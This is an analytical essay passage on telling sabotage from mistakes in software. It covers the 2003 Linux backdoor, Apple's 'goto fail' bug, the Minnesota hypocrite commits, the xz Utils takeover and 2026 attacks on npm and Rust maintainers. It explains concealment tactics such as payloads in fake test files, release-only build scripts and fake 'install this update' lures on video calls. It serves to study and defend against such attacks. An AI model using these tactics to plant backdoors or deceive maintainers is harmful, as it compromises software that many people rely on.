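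Typing one equals sign instead of two is one of the best-known mistakes in C, and it is easy to overlook. Chad Kitching pointed out the backdoor 25 minutes after McVoy posted the lines, and McVoy replied, "Good eyes, I missed that."

### Why the route mattered more than the code

The lines themselves contain some clues. Kitching noticed that the check would have been useless even with both equals signs, because the next line of the program overwrote the error code. A commenter on computer scientist Ed Felten's *The Linux Backdoor Attempt of 2003* (Freedom to Tinker, 2013) added that the combination of options is harmless and that there was no reason to forbid only root from using it. Both observations are some evidence of deliberate design, because someone who makes an honest mistake is usually trying to do something useful. They are not conclusive, since honest programmers write useless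 checks too.

The extra parentheses around `current->uid = 0` are weaker evidence of intent than they first seem. Tomas Szepe pointed to these parentheses, which keep the compiler (the program that translates the code for the machine) from warning about a likely mistake. But many programmers add them anyway to make the line easier to read, so someone who dropped an equals sign by mistake could have left the same parentheses.

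The better evidence was the record of where the lines came from and who had approved them. In a later message, McVoy (2003) explained that every night a BitMover program exported the master copy to CVS on a machine inside the company, copied the changed files to the public server, and compared checksums, which are short numbers calculated from the contents of the files. The lines were in the public copy but not the internal one, so they must have been added on the public server.

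McVoy first looked for an innocent cause, spending part of the day testing whether his own export program had gone wrong. This was sensible because software faults are far more common than intrusions. But the tests found no evidence that the program was at fault, and a faulty export was very unlikely to produce a grammatical line of C.

That left the possibility that a developer had taken a shortcut. A commenter on Freedom to Tinker defended this explanation, describing exhausted programmers who bypass review at four in the morning to meet a deadline. But nothing placed in the CVS copy could get back into the master copy, so an honest developer gained nothing by editing it and had no reason to do so under Miller's name. Nobody in the thread accepted McVoy's invitation to admit making the edit, either.

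Some invented numbers show how much the route adds to the case for deliberate design. Suppose that one in 10,000 wrong equals signs in properly submitted code is deliberate, and that the clues in these lines are 100 times as probable from an attacker as from a careless programmer. The odds of deliberate design are then about 1 to 100, so a slip is still much more likely. Now suppose that one attacker in ten would edit the public copy under somebody else's name, compared with one careless programmer in a million. This multiplies the odds by 100,000, to 1,000 to 1 in favour of deliberate design. If the figure for attackers were ten times lower and the figure for careless programmers ten times higher, the odds would still be 10 to 1 in favour of deliberate design.

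The actual investigation followed the same order. According to *The upcoming security fight*, published that November on the Linux news site LWN, the missing pointer raised the suspicion and the code then confirmed it.

Nobody found out who did it. Felten thought it could have been the National Security Agency (NSA), the American signals intelligence agency, but many others also had the skill and the motive. He expected never to know unless someone confessed or a document surfaced. LWN suspected a publicity stunt by someone who wanted to embarrass free software, because the backdoor was useful only to an attacker who could already run programs on the machine. The evidence showed that the backdoor was deliberate but did not establish its purpose. LWN's explanation is a guess, and nothing in the file's history supports it over espionage.

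People also disagreed about how close the attempt came to succeeding. Linus Torvalds, who created Linux and controls the master copy, said the lines could not have reached a release, because changes reached him only by email or through BitKeeper, and BitKeeper users would not have touched the CVS copy. McVoy was less sure. He thought a programmer working from the CVS copy could have emailed in a patch (a proposed change) containing the planted lines. A reader of LWN's *An attempt to backdoor the kernel* (2003) described how this might happen. After BitMover's program restored the public file, CVS could treat the planted lines still on the programmer's machine as the programmer's own work. Another reader replied that nobody who used CVS correctly would have this problem.

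If that had happened, Torvalds would have received the lines from an honest developer, under the developer's own name. No evidence of their route would have remained, and anyone who later noticed that an equals sign was missing would have had good reason to call it a typo.

### Apple's duplicated line

Investigators of a flaw that Apple repaired in February 2014 had to manage without that kind of evidence. The flaw was in the code that iPhones and Macs used to confirm the identity of secure websites. The code carried out a series of checks, each followed by the instruction `goto fail`, which told the computer to jump to the end if the check had failed. In one place the instruction appeared twice in a row:

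```
if ((err = SSLHashSHA1.update(&hashCtx, &signedParams)) != 0)
    goto fail;
    goto fail;
```

Only the first `goto fail` depended on the condition above it. Despite its indentation, the second ran whenever the program reached it, so the program jumped to the end and skipped the check of the website's signature. Because no earlier check had failed, the code reported success. Someone who controlled a café's network could have posed as a customer's bank.

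Many people suspected sabotage. Edward Snowden had leaked documents about NSA surveillance the year before, and one slide dated Apple's entry into the agency's PRISM programme to October 2012, a few weeks after Apple released the first iPhone software with the flaw. The timing is weaker evidence than it looks, because PRISM obtained data from companies under legal orders and so did not require a flaw in the iPhone. People who look for a suspicious date near a software release will also often find one. Adam Langley, a Google engineer who published an early analysis of the code, believed the flaw was just a mistake.

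Apple has never publicly explained how the second line got there. The usual guesses are that a programmer pasted a line twice, or that a tool for merging two versions of the file kept a line from each. Either mistake would produce exactly this text, but so could a saboteur inside Apple, who could then have called it an accident.

Both flaws were tiny and disastrous, and both could pass for mistakes, but outsiders know different things about how each got into the code. The duplicated line reached the public in an ordinary Apple release, where one would expect to find either an employee's mistake or an employee's sabotage. The likelihood ratio is therefore close to 1, so the verdict depends on the prior odds, which favour a mistake because editing accidents are so common. Apple's own records could provide better evidence, since they would show who made the edit, what else changed at the same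 time, and who reviewed it.

### The hypocrite commits of 2020

The second deception came from people the kernel's maintainers already knew. Starting in 2018, a research group at the University of Minnesota led by Kangjie Lu submitted about 400 bug fixes to the kernel, most of them connected with papers on finding errors automatically. In 2020 Lu and Qiushi Wu, another member of the group, wanted to show that an attacker could slip a vulnerability into open-source software with a "hypocrite commit", a change that seems to fix a small problem while introducing a worse one.

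They sent their patches under two invented names, "James Bond" and "George Acosta". According to the paper's section on ethics, which Gunthorpe (2021) quoted on the mailing list, they meant to demonstrate a danger without harming anyone, and took care to keep the flawed code from being merged. But they did mean to deceive the reviewers, which is enough to make this malice in the sense used here.

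The fullest record is *Report on University of Minnesota Breach-of-Trust Incident* (Mason, Rostedt and colleagues, 2021), an audit by the Technical Advisory Board of the Linux Foundation, the non-profit that supports kernel development. The audit traced five patches sent under the false names.

| Sent in August 2020 | Name | What the patch was | What happened |
|---|---|---|---|
| 4 August | James Bond | An honest fix, according to the researchers | The maintainer ignored it |
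| 9 August | James Bond | A copy of an earlier bad patch | Maintainers rejected it |
| 20 August | George Acosta | Meant to be flawed, but correct | The maintainer accepted it |
| 20 August | George Acosta | Flawed | A reviewer caught it and suggested corrections |
| 21 August | James Bond | Flawed | The maintainer caught it and the sender apologised |

Of the five patches, the one that got in was a valid improvement, though its senders had set out to deceive and to break something. They failed because they misunderstood how the kernel handles drivers for a common type of hardware.

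The patch of 4 August seems to have been the opposite. The researchers said it belonged to a separate project and went out under the name "James Bond" only because they had already set up a computer for the deception. Mason and colleagues found some support for this. The patch altered a function on the bug list of another of the group's papers, and somebody in the group had tried to fix the same function in June under a real name. Reading the code would not have revealed the sender's intentions in either case.

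Mason and colleagues concluded that the review process had worked, since maintainers caught or ignored every invalid patch. But so few patches are weak evidence that maintainers would catch the next one. At least one of the three bad patches was also easy to catch, because it copied a patch already notorious among kernel developers.

### The patches of April 2021

The study drew complaints about its ethics as soon as the paper appeared in November 2020, and the group then sent no patches to the kernel for months. On 6 April 2021 Aditya Pakki, one of Lu's students, began sending patches again, but they were poor. One set a variable to zero just before the function ended, when nothing could use it any more, and then checked for a condition that could not arise.

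Greg Kroah-Hartman, who maintains the kernel's stable releases, told Pakki to stop experimenting on the maintainers. Pakki answered that the patches came from a new static analyser he had written, a program that looks for likely bugs in code without running it. He admitted that the analyser was not very good and said he had hoped for feedback. He also objected that Kroah-Hartman's accusations bordered on slander and gave him no benefit of the doubt.

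Kroah-Hartman (2021) replied on 21 April with several reasons for not believing Pakki. Pakki's group had publicly admitted to sending patches it knew to be bad. The new patches followed such different patterns that no competent tool could have produced them all. People who send patches found by a tool normally say so and ask for advice, but Pakki had presented his as real fixes. Anyone who knew a little C could see within minutes that they did nothing. Kroah-Hartman announced that he would ban all contributions from the university and remove its earlier ones, which he said its people had "obviously submitted in bad-faith".

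Later that day Lu wrote that the deception study had finished in November 2020 and that Pakki was working on a separate project to find bugs introduced by patches. Lu admitted that Pakki's patches were wrong but said the mistakes were not deliberate.

Kroah-Hartman's first reason is a good reason to be suspicious at first. The others mostly show that the patches were bad, which both sides accepted. To choose between the explanations, we have to compare Pakki's patches with what a second experiment would have looked like. The first experiment used false names and private email accounts, and its patches were supposed to look useful while containing real vulnerabilities. Five months after the scandal, Pakki sent useless and mostly harmless patches under his own name from his university address. They could still have been part of a new study of whether reviewers accept nonsense, but it would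 have been foolish to run that study from the one address that maintainers had learned to distrust.

Suppose, with invented numbers, that after 2020 the odds were as high as 1 to 4 that a new batch of bad patches from this group was another experiment. Compared with honest work, an experiment is perhaps a tenth as likely to carry a real name and address, half as likely to contain harmless patches, and three times as likely to leave the tool unmentioned. Together these clues multiply the odds by 0.15, to about 1 to 27, or a probability of 3.6%. For a group with no history of deception, starting at 1 to 10,000, the same clues would leave a probability of 0.0015%. The 2020 study therefore makes a second deception more than 2,000 times as likely as it would otherwise have been, but incompetence is still a much more likely explanation.

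The history also changed how people read older work. Guenter Roeck, another maintainer, pointed to a commit by Lu that had introduced a bug into a hardware sensor driver. Roeck (2021) wrote that he had to assume Lu had done it on purpose, and that Lu had therefore lied in saying publicly that the experiment had put no bugs into open-source software. But the commit dates from December 2018, more than a year and a half before the first false name. In the closing part of the *Report on University of Minnesota Breach-of-Trust Incident*, the Board lists it as an incorrect fix that another developer had already repaired. The bug was real and Lu had deceived the maintainers, but Roeck connected the two without checking the date.

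### What the audit found

Kroah-Hartman began removing the university's work by posting 190 reverts, which undo earlier changes. In that message he called the submissions "almost universally wrong". Mason and colleagues, with help from dozens of other developers, re-reviewed 435 commits and found that 349 (80%) were correct.

Another 39 needed fixing or replacing, including the "George Acosta" patch, which worked but had to be removed because the kernel does not accept contributions under false names. Other developers had already repaired another 25, and one had been removed at its author's request. The remaining 21 were either obsolete or older than the research group. About 15% were therefore faulty, but Mason and colleagues did not re-review a comparable set of commits from anyone else, so there is no baseline for that figure. Al Viro, a veteran kernel developer who had followed the reviews,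 said in *A statement on the UMN mess* (2021) that he had seen nothing plausibly malicious and thought the quality was more or less usual.

The Board distinguished patches by intent, with separate labels for an "incorrect fix" and an "attempted hypocrite commit". It gave the second label only to the "Acosta" patch, the only one of the five to enter the kernel. It classed the April 2021 commit that Pakki had asked to withdraw as an incorrect fix. Cook (2021) had already written on the Board's behalf, the day after the ban, that the vast majority of the university's patches seemed to have been in good faith. Kroah-Hartman was a member of the Board, which makes its findings in the researchers' favour more credible.

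The auditors had no direct way to know what anyone had intended. They relied partly on the researchers' own disclosure for the list of deceptive patches, though it matched the emails that outsiders had already identified. A well-disguised vulnerability might also have passed as correct code a second time. But the audit found nothing to support the specific accusation that the group had kept experimenting in 2021 and had sent its earlier work in bad faith.

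The researchers had apologised by then in an open letter, quoted in Slashdot's *University of Minnesota Researchers Send Apology to Linux Kernel Mailing List*. They said they had meant to improve the security of Linux and now understood that it was hurtful to make the community a subject of research without its permission. Machek (2021), a kernel developer who had opposed the mass revert from the start, asked after the audit whether the maintainers owed an apology too, since there had been no deception in 2021. Cook agreed that Kroah-Hartman's wording should have distinguished intentional flaws from unintentional ones, and left the question of an apology to him.

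### How far one deception should raise suspicion

Maintainers were right to recheck everything the group had sent, since even 3.6% is far above any plausible threshold for a review. The review also uncovered dozens of honest errors that had been in the kernel for years.

Reverting the commits before reviewing them was harder to justify, because most of them fixed real bugs that would have come back. Gunthorpe feared that the giant revert would degrade the kernel more than the experimenters had. In practice, it served as a request for review. Developers objected to 24 of the 190 reverts almost at once. Theodore Ts'o, another Board member, explained in the comments on LWN's *The TAB report on the UMN affair* (2021) that Kroah-Hartman dropped each revert whose original commit turned out to be valid. The public charge of bad faith came before this review, although it needed a far higher probability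 of malice to justify it than the review did.

A reader in the same discussion took a position close to Grey's law. He wrote that the new patches were sent in good faith but were so bad that nobody could tell them from patches sent in bad faith, and that maintainers had no duty to put up with them either way. That is a fair reason to stop accepting the patches, but it doesn't support calling Pakki a liar. Kroah-Hartman had done both in one email.

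The case for raising the prior odds is strongest for Wu and Lu, who had carried out the deception. Pakki belonged to their group but was not an author of the study. The ban covered the whole university, and the audit, which searched by email address, included nine commits from 2006 and 2013 by people who had nothing to do with Lu's research. But a submitter can easily avoid using a university address. Viro pointed out that the bulk revert would have missed any sock puppets, and the 2020 patches had come from Gmail accounts. The audit also missed a visiting student who had sent four patches from a private address. The University of Minnesota added the student in its *Statement from Computer Science & Engineering confirming Linux Technical Advisory Board findings* (2021).

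Roeck drew the widest conclusion, writing that maintainers now had to assume that contributions were malicious and that he would be less inclined to accept small fixes from people he didn't know. One university's experiment had thus made contributing harder for people unconnected with it. This kind of suspicion also does little against a patient attacker who first earns the maintainers' trust, as one did in the xz Utils takeover.

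Mason and colleagues made a more modest recommendation, that the university find at least one experienced developer to check its patches before anyone sent them to the kernel. Such a reviewer would have stopped many of the careless patches and might have talked Lu and Wu out of the 2020 study before it began.

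## The campaign to take over xz Utils

xz Utils is a free set of tools for compressing files, and most Linux systems include it. Lasse Collin had maintained it since 2009, unpaid and largely alone. In February 2024 his co-maintainer, who went by the name Jia Tan, released a version with a backdoor. Had that version spread, the backdoor's owner could have run any command on a vast number of servers without logging in. Tan had worked on the project for more than two years by then. In 2022, while Tan was still a newcomer, two other accounts had pressed Collin to hand over control. Russ Cox, a researcher at Google, reconstructed the campaign in *Timeline of the xz open source attack* (2024).

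### A helpful newcomer and two impatient users

Tan's first patch, sent to the xz mailing list on 29 October 2021, added a small file of settings for text editors. Other minor patches followed, and Cox finds nothing wrong with them even in retrospect. An honest volunteer might well have started this way, and so might an attacker who wanted Collin's trust, so Collin couldn't tell from the quality of the patches which one he was dealing with.

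The complaints began in April 2022, when an account named Jigar Kumar objected that one of Tan's patches was still waiting, although Collin had already accepted four others. In May an account named Dennis Ens asked whether anyone still maintained the Java version of xz. Collin apologised for his slowness and wrote that Tan had been helping him privately and might have a bigger role in future.

The tone got worse in June, when Kumar told Ens that nothing would happen until there was a new maintainer. Collin answered that he hadn't lost interest, but that long-term mental health problems limited what he could do, and that xz was an unpaid hobby. Securelist's *Assessing the Y, and How, of the XZ Utils incident* reprints the reply in which Ens expressed sympathy about Collin's health but said "the community desires more" and suggested handing over one of the two versions. A day later Kumar asked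 Tan on the list why Tan couldn't commit the patch directly. On 29 June Collin wrote that Tan was "practically a co-maintainer already".

The innocent reading was that the emails came from real users who were rude. People who depend on free software do complain when it stalls, and Collin agreed that he had too little time. But as one would expect in an attack, the emails asked for a new maintainer rather than for particular repairs, and they arrived when a willing replacement was available. The accounts' disappearance once Tan had the job also fits an attack, but Collin couldn't have known about that in June 2022.

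Cox writes that the pressure worked, which is plausible but hard to prove. Collin had mentioned a bigger role for Tan on 19 May, before the harshest emails arrived, so the campaign may only have sped up a decision he was already making.

### Two complainers or one?

The odds form of Bayes' rule shows how much depended on who was behind the complaints. All the numbers here are invented. The starting odds are 1 to 10,000 that a stranger who sends a first patch to a project like xz is an attacker.

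Tan was still sending patches eight months later. Suppose that one honest newcomer in ten lasts that long, and that half of attackers do, because they have to keep going to get what they want. The likelihood ratio is then 5, and the odds that Tan is an attacker rise to 1 to 2,000. Diligence therefore counts slightly against Tan, but a newcomer who lasts that long is still 2,000 times as likely to be honest as to be an attacker.

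Suppose that Kumar and Ens were real users with no connection to Tan or to each other. Each was in effect recommending that Collin rely on Tan. If real users are half as likely to recommend a volunteer who is an attacker, the two recommendations together have a likelihood ratio of 1/4, and the odds that Tan is an attacker fall to 1 to 8,000.

Suppose instead that one person wrote all the complaints while posing as two strangers. Perhaps one attacker in ten would try this. An honest newcomer or an overeager friend might do it in one case in 20,000. The likelihood ratio is then 0.1 / 0.00005 = 2,000, and the odds become even.

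| Evidence | Likelihood ratio | Odds that Tan is an attacker | Probability |
|---|---|---|---|
| None yet | | 1 to 10,000 | 0.01% |
| Eight months of steady patches | 5 | 1 to 2,000 | 0.05% |
| The patches, and complaints from two unconnected users | 1/4 | 1 to 8,000 | 0.01% |
| The patches, and complaints from one person with two accounts | 2,000 | 1 to 1 | 50% |

The same emails either slightly lower the probability that Tan is an attacker or raise it to about 50%, and the odds in the two cases differ by a factor of 8,000. The figure of one in 20,000 is the least certain. If the true figure is ten times higher, the probability in the last row falls to 9%, which is still hundreds of times the probability in the row above.

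Collin didn't know which situation he was in, so he would have had to allow for both. Suppose that two unconnected users complain like this in 5% of cases where the newcomer is honest, and so in 1.25% of cases where the newcomer is an attacker. Adding the chance that one person wrote everything gives a likelihood ratio of

$$\frac{0.1 + 0.0125}{0.00005 + 0.05} \approx 2.2$$

The odds are then about 1 to 890, or a probability of about 0.1%. The complaints should have roughly doubled Collin's suspicion of Tan, but it would still have been very low, because impatient users are common and plots like this one are rare. Cox thinks the xz attack was the first serious known attack of its kind on widely used open-source software.

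Looking up the email addresses would have told Collin more. The security journalist Brian Krebs later observed that many of them had never appeared anywhere else on the internet, even in stolen data. Suppose that one real user in five has an address like that, so that two unconnected users both have one in 4% of cases, while sock puppets always do. The likelihood ratio becomes

$$\frac{0.1 + 0.0005}{0.00005 + 0.002} \approx 49$$

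and the probability that Tan is an attacker rises to 2.4%. That is far too low for an accusation, but it might have justified asking an established developer to share the maintainer's role. Still, hardly any maintainer investigates the people who complain to them, and we know that this search was worth making only because we know how the story ended.

### The handover and the groundwork

Collin gave up control in stages. Tan joined the project's organisation on GitHub, a code-hosting site, in October 2022. In November Collin redirected bug reports to an address that reached both of them, and by the end of December Tan was adding commits directly. Collin made his last release in January 2023, and Tan made his first in March. Tan also arranged to receive the bug reports from oss-fuzz, a Google service that tests open-source programs for errors by feeding them random data.

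In *Wolves in the Repository*, Przymus and Durieux (2025) examined 1,020 commits and 307 mailing-list messages from the project and found that Tan worked more on documentation and translations than on code. Tan also answered users' questions, announced releases and put a personal email address on the form for reporting problems. An overworked maintainer badly needs this help, but it is just as useful to an attacker, because whoever receives the bug reports can decide how to answer them and who else hears about them.

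In June 2023 an account named Hans Jansen contributed patches that used "indirect functions", a feature that lets a program choose between several versions of a function as it starts. The stated purpose was to make xz faster by letting it pick the version best suited to the processor. Collin reworked the last of the patches and Tan merged it. The backdoor later used this feature to run its own code before the system locked the table a program uses to find its functions. In July Tan switched the feature off in the oss-fuzz tests, saying that it clashed with another testing tool.

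Even now these changes are ambiguous. Cox thinks either change could have been innocent on its own, and Przymus and Durieux say it remains unclear whether Jansen's patches were a genuine improvement. A reviewer in 2023 had less evidence, because the code that would misuse the feature hadn't been added yet.

### The backdoored releases

The target was OpenSSH, the program administrators use to log in to distant machines. OpenSSH doesn't use xz itself, but Debian, Fedora and some other Linux distributions had modified it to work with systemd, the software that starts a system's services, and systemd's library loaded the xz library.

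On 23 February 2024 Tan hid most of the backdoor in files that looked like test data. A compression library needs damaged and unusual files for testing, and the project's notes had long said that many were handmade, so the new ones didn't look suspicious. Reviewers also can't read such files the way they read code. Version 5.6.0, released the next day, contained the rest of the backdoor, an altered script that unpacked the hidden code when somebody built xz for Debian or Fedora. The script was in the release package Tan published but not in the public repository. Release packages often contain extra scripts, so this difference didn't look suspicious either.

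Version 5.6.0 didn't use the new files in any test. This was visible from the start and odd, because someone who adds a test file normally wants to test something. The useless check in the lines planted in the kernel was odd in a similar way.

The backdoor also had bugs. In early March, users of Red Hat's distributions saw errors from Valgrind, a tool that detects memory errors in programs. Tan published a supposed fix on 8 March, which Cox calls a misdirection, and removed the errors the next day by replacing the two test files. Tan said that the old files contained random data from one machine and that the new ones would be easier to reproduce. Tan was feigning incompetence by presenting a repair to the backdoor as a maintainer's correction of a careless release. This was convincing because new releases often have bugs. Version 5.6.0 also had an ordinary bug, which Tan fixed the same week.

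Another change in late February contained a small typo that prevented xz from using Landlock, a Linux feature for restricting what a program may do. Like the missing equals sign of 2003, the typo could pass for a slip. It was much more likely deliberate, because Tan was planting a backdoor that same week, but Cox can't say what the typo was for.

Tan then had reason to hurry, because on 29 February a developer proposed that systemd's library stop loading the xz library, which would have defeated the attack. The security researcher Kevin Beaumont speculates that the attacker knew this change was coming. In late March Jansen reappeared after nine months and asked Debian to adopt version 5.6.1. Two more unknown accounts supported the request within a couple of days, one saying the new version would solve its problem with Valgrind. When a Debian developer objected to the procedure, the same account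 replied that fixing the fault mattered more than debating policy. Debian updated xz on 27 March.

### Half a second

The next day Andres Freund, a PostgreSQL database developer at Microsoft, warned Debian privately. Over several weeks he had noticed Valgrind errors and logins that used too much processor time. His public report, *backdoor in upstream xz/liblzma leading to ssh server compromise* (Freund, 2024), lists times for a failed login of 0.299 seconds without the new library and 0.807 seconds with it. The extra half second came from the backdoor searching lists of function names in memory.

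Slow software usually has an innocent cause, and Freund didn't begin by accusing Tan. He traced the delay to the xz library and at first thought that someone had tampered only with Debian's copy. He ruled that out when he found the altered script in the project's own release packages.

He also considered whether somebody had broken into Tan's computer, but thought this less likely because Tan had been writing to several mailing lists about the "fixes". An intruder would have had to write those emails too, for weeks, without Tan noticing.

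Debian withdrew the new version at once. It had mostly reached test editions, including a beta of Fedora 40, and Przymus and Durieux know of no case where anyone used the backdoor.

### Signs of coordination

The accounts left no trace elsewhere, and most used free email addresses made of a name and a number. Securelist also finds similar misspellings and grammatical mistakes in the emails from Tan, Kumar and Ens. These clues are weaker evidence than their number suggests, because they aren't independent. A real user who values privacy might open a new free account just for a mailing list, which would explain the missing history, the provider and perhaps the number in the address.

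Timing is also a weaker clue than it looks. Przymus and Durieux count eight new people on the mailing list during the months of pressure, when 29 had been active before, and six of the eight wrote only in that period. But they report that only two of the newcomers pressured Collin, so most of the six did nothing suspicious. The project also moved to GitHub that December, which gave everyone a reason to leave the list.

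The shared demands are better evidence, because Kumar and Ens supported each other and wanted the same remedy, which suited Tan. The best evidence is that Jansen supplied the feature the backdoor needed and came back nine months later to promote the release that contained the backdoor. An honest programmer might have done either, but Jansen did both, had no other activity anywhere, and was supported by two more untraceable accounts. That combination is hard to explain unless Jansen was working with Tan.

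Securelist sets out three possible explanations: a small team ran the whole campaign, one person ran it, or Tan earned the position honestly and others manipulated Tan in early 2024, while Kumar and Ens had complained by coincidence. The third explanation can't easily account for Jansen's patches of 2023. The clues do little to distinguish a team from an individual, since we would expect shared habits and demands from either. Przymus and Durieux found no direct links between the accounts, so coordination is an inference from how the accounts behaved, though a strong one.

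### Judging Collin with hindsight

The 2022 emails look obviously staged to anyone who knows about the backdoor. Psychologists call this hindsight bias, the tendency to see an outcome as more predictable than it was. A fair judgement of Collin has to take into account how often the same signs appear in projects where nothing bad happens.

They probably appear often. Przymus and Durieux mention rapid changes in Tan's expertise and an unusual amount of time spent on the project, but admit that keen and skilled volunteers often show the same signs. Only eight of Tan's hundreds of commits were malicious. With the invented numbers above, a maintainer who turned away every volunteer in Tan's position would lose about 890 honest helpers for each attacker. Collin's realistic alternative was to carry on alone, and neglected software has security problems too.

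In 2022, Lasse Collin could have noticed that Kumar, in his first complaint, ignored the four patches Collin had accepted, and that the complainers had no history. He could not have known that they would vanish, that Jansen would return, or what the new feature was for. By 2024, the most useful check was to compare each release package with the public repository and ask about every unexplained difference. This required no opinion about Tan and would have exposed the altered script. Arch Linux began building xz straight from the repository on the day of Freund's private warning. Building this way leaves out the backdoor's trigger, although the test files that hid the rest of the backdoor were in the repository too.

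According to an alert the Linux Foundation published about similar takeover attempts, good support for maintainers is the primary deterrent. That fits this case, since the pressure on Collin was believable because he really was overworked, and a second trusted maintainer would have made the pressure pointless.

### Who was Jia Tan?

The public evidence doesn't identify the person or people behind the name Jia Tan. In April 2024, Colomar (2024) tried to work out Tan's possible employer from the history of the code in *Analysis on who is Jia Tan, and who he could work for*. Within three days, another programmer's script had revealed a mistake in the timestamp analysis, which Colomar acknowledged in a message quoted by Bachmeyer (2024) under the same title. Timestamps can also mislead because an attacker can set a computer's clock to any time zone.

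Securelist traced one connection that may have been Tan's to an address in Singapore, but the address belonged to a VPN, which hides its users' locations. The attackers' names suggest people from Southeast Asia, India and northern Europe, and Securelist suspects that the attackers chose them to look unconnected. A researcher called Alden found that Tan made the malicious commits at unusual hours. That might mean that a second person was using the account, a team was working in shifts, or one person was in a hurry.

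The campaign's length suggests a patient sponsor such as a government, but less strongly than many people assume, because volunteers like Collin do years of skilled work on open-source projects without a sponsor.

### Looking for the next Jia Tan

*Wolves in the Repository* recommends tracking how contributors' expertise and involvement change over time. It also proposes crediting automated improvements to the tool that made them, so that people can't easily build trust by running a spelling checker or a language model. *Beneath the Mask* (2025) uses contribution data to try to automate the search for behaviour like Tan's in other projects, which it says nobody had yet tried. *Towards Socio-Technical Topology-Aware Adaptive Threat Detection in Software Supply Chains* (2025) divides the xz campaign into legitimate contributions, escalation of control and deployment of the backdoor, and looks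 for both social and technical warning signs.

Such attackers are hard to detect because they are rare. Suppose that one contributor in 10,000 is an attacker, and that a detector flags 90% of attackers and 1% of honest people. Among 10,000 contributors, it would flag about 100 honest people and at most one attacker, so fewer than 1% of its flags would be correct. The detector could help a project decide whose releases get an extra check, but not whom to ban. Attackers can also read the research and avoid repeating what Tan did.

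### The Axios compromise

In 2026, attackers got similar access in weeks by taking over the computer of someone users already trusted. Their target was Axios, a library that JavaScript programs use to communicate over the web. Developers download it about 100 million times a week from npm, the main public collection of JavaScript packages.

Jason Saayman, its lead maintainer, described the deception in an account quoted in *Axios Supply-Chain Attack* (Solar Designer, 2026). About two weeks before the attack, someone posing as the founder of a real company invited him to a Slack workspace. It had the company's branding, channels full of its LinkedIn posts, and what he presumes were fake profiles of its staff and of other open-source maintainers. He then joined a video meeting on Microsoft Teams with what seemed to be several people. He saw a message that something on his system was out of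 date. He assumed it had to do with Teams and installed the missing item, a program that gave the attackers control of his computer.

On 31 March they used his account to publish two versions of Axios that installed similar malware on other people's machines. Users reported the problem within the hour, but the attackers used his account to delete the reports. Another Axios developer raised the alarm, and npm removed both versions about three hours after the first appeared.

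Anyone who saw only the account name would have blamed Saayman. Freund's reasoning about Tan leads to the opposite conclusion about Saayman, because Tan had defended the malicious releases for weeks, while Saayman's account hid the evidence for a few hours and he then explained in detail how he had been fooled. According to Infosecurity Magazine's *Hackers Hijack Axios npm Package to Spread RATs*, the attackers also bypassed the automated process that signed real Axios releases and published theirs directly with stolen credentials.

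Google attributed the attack to UNC1069, a North Korean group that steals for profit, because the malware was a newer version of a program the group had used before. *AWS Blames North Korean Group for npm Supply Chain Attacks* (Muncaster, 2026) reported that AWS, Amazon's cloud business, also blamed a North Korean group in July. Shared malware is much better evidence than a name or a time zone, but it isn't proof, because one group can steal or buy another's tools.

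### When the targets compared notes

After Saayman told his story, other maintainers recognised it, and The Hacker News (2026) collected several of their accounts. Pelle Wessman, who helps maintain the testing tool Mocha, accepted a podcast invitation that led him to a fake copy of a recording website. The site showed a believable error and offered an app to fix it. He refused, and the hosts asked him to run a command instead. When he refused that too, they erased every conversation and disappeared. Jean Burellier, who works on Node.js (software for running JavaScript on servers), got a similar request to update Teams. When he declined and suggested another day for the call, the callers removed him from their Slack workspaces and deleted the messages.

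The staged fault made malice look like a mistake that nobody in particular had made. Video calls often fail, and programs often ask for updates. Suppose, again with invented numbers, that one unsolicited business contact in 500 is an attacker, and that one honest first call in 20 leads to a request to install something. If attackers always make the request, receiving one raises the odds of an attack to 1 to 25, or about 4%. A maintainer who goes by the most likely explanation will install the update, but one who weighs the consequences will refuse, because refusing means a little awkwardness and a rescheduled call, while the malware could reach millions of people.

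Now two colleagues report the same thing from other companies. If each report is also 20 times as likely when there is a campaign, the odds rise to 16 to 1, a probability of 94%. This assumes that honest faults are independent, but a bad Teams update could affect everybody in the same week. Maintainers who ask enough colleagues will also find somebody whose call went wrong. The deleted conversations help with both problems, because a software fault doesn't erase a Slack workspace after a guest declines an update. A real company would also have accepted Burellier's offer of another day.

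In the xz campaign, one source had looked like several unconnected people. In 2026, each target saw what looked like an isolated fault, and they discovered the common source only when they compared what they had seen.

The accounts also differ on whether the attackers rush their targets. Matteo Collina, who maintains several widely used packages, nearly fell for the same scheme. His newsletter article *Why “Trusted Publishing” Can’t Save Us from Social Engineering* (Adventures in Nodeland, 2026) lists an unknown domain, a direct download link and pressure for immediate action among the warning signs. But a researcher quoted in Hackread's *UNC1069 Targets Node.js Maintainers via Fake LinkedIn, Slack Profiles* described an unhurried approach, in which the callers would schedule a meeting for the following week and then postpone it by another week. Someone who watches only for urgency would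 miss this version. Every account includes a request to run something on the target's own computer, so that request is a better warning sign than the caller's manner.

Comparing notes also requires people to be willing to admit they were fooled. In Security.NL's *Meerdere Node.js maintainers doelwit van social engineering-aanvallen*, a researcher urges victims and targets to keep sharing their stories, and urges others to protect them from people who call them stupid. Mocking victims in hindsight is unfair, and it also discourages the reports that would warn the next target.

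### The approaches to Rust developers

Developers of the programming language Rust reported the same kind of approach that summer. In *Anatomy of a Failed (Nation-State?) Attack* (June 2026), a maintainer described a fake job interview meant to plant a backdoor on his machine and said others in the Rust community had mentioned being targets too. On 20 August attackers published malicious versions of three Rust packages, including the popular arrayref. The new versions relied on another package, proc-macro1, which downloaded malware (Goregaokar, *Supply chain attack on arrayref*, 2026). McCarthy and Read point out in *Rust Supply Chain Attack on arrayref* (2026) that arrayref had not relied on any other package in its ten-year history, so the change was conspicuous to anyone who looked.

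In September, *Be alert* (Harvey, 2026) warned on behalf of the Rust project about video calls in which the caller asks the target to install a supposedly missing audio codec, a component that decodes sound. The evidence for North Korean involvement varies between these cases. McCarthy and Read found that the arrayref attackers used some of the same infrastructure as the Axios attackers. For the September calls, *Rust Team Members and Popular Crate Owners Targeted via Video Calls* (Kovacs, 2026) reports only that the techniques match. The press had already described those techniques in detail by then, so any criminal could have copied them.

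The prior odds of malice had changed, whoever was responsible. Help Net Security's *North Korea’s job interview scam runs both ways* (2026) reports that authorities in several countries estimate one North Korean group infected more than 30,000 devices through fake interviews and similar approaches between December 2025 and July 2026. Nobody has counted the honest approaches in the same period, so the figure doesn't give the odds that any one message is malicious. But it makes it much harder for a maintainer to defend the old assumption that such things hardly ever happen.

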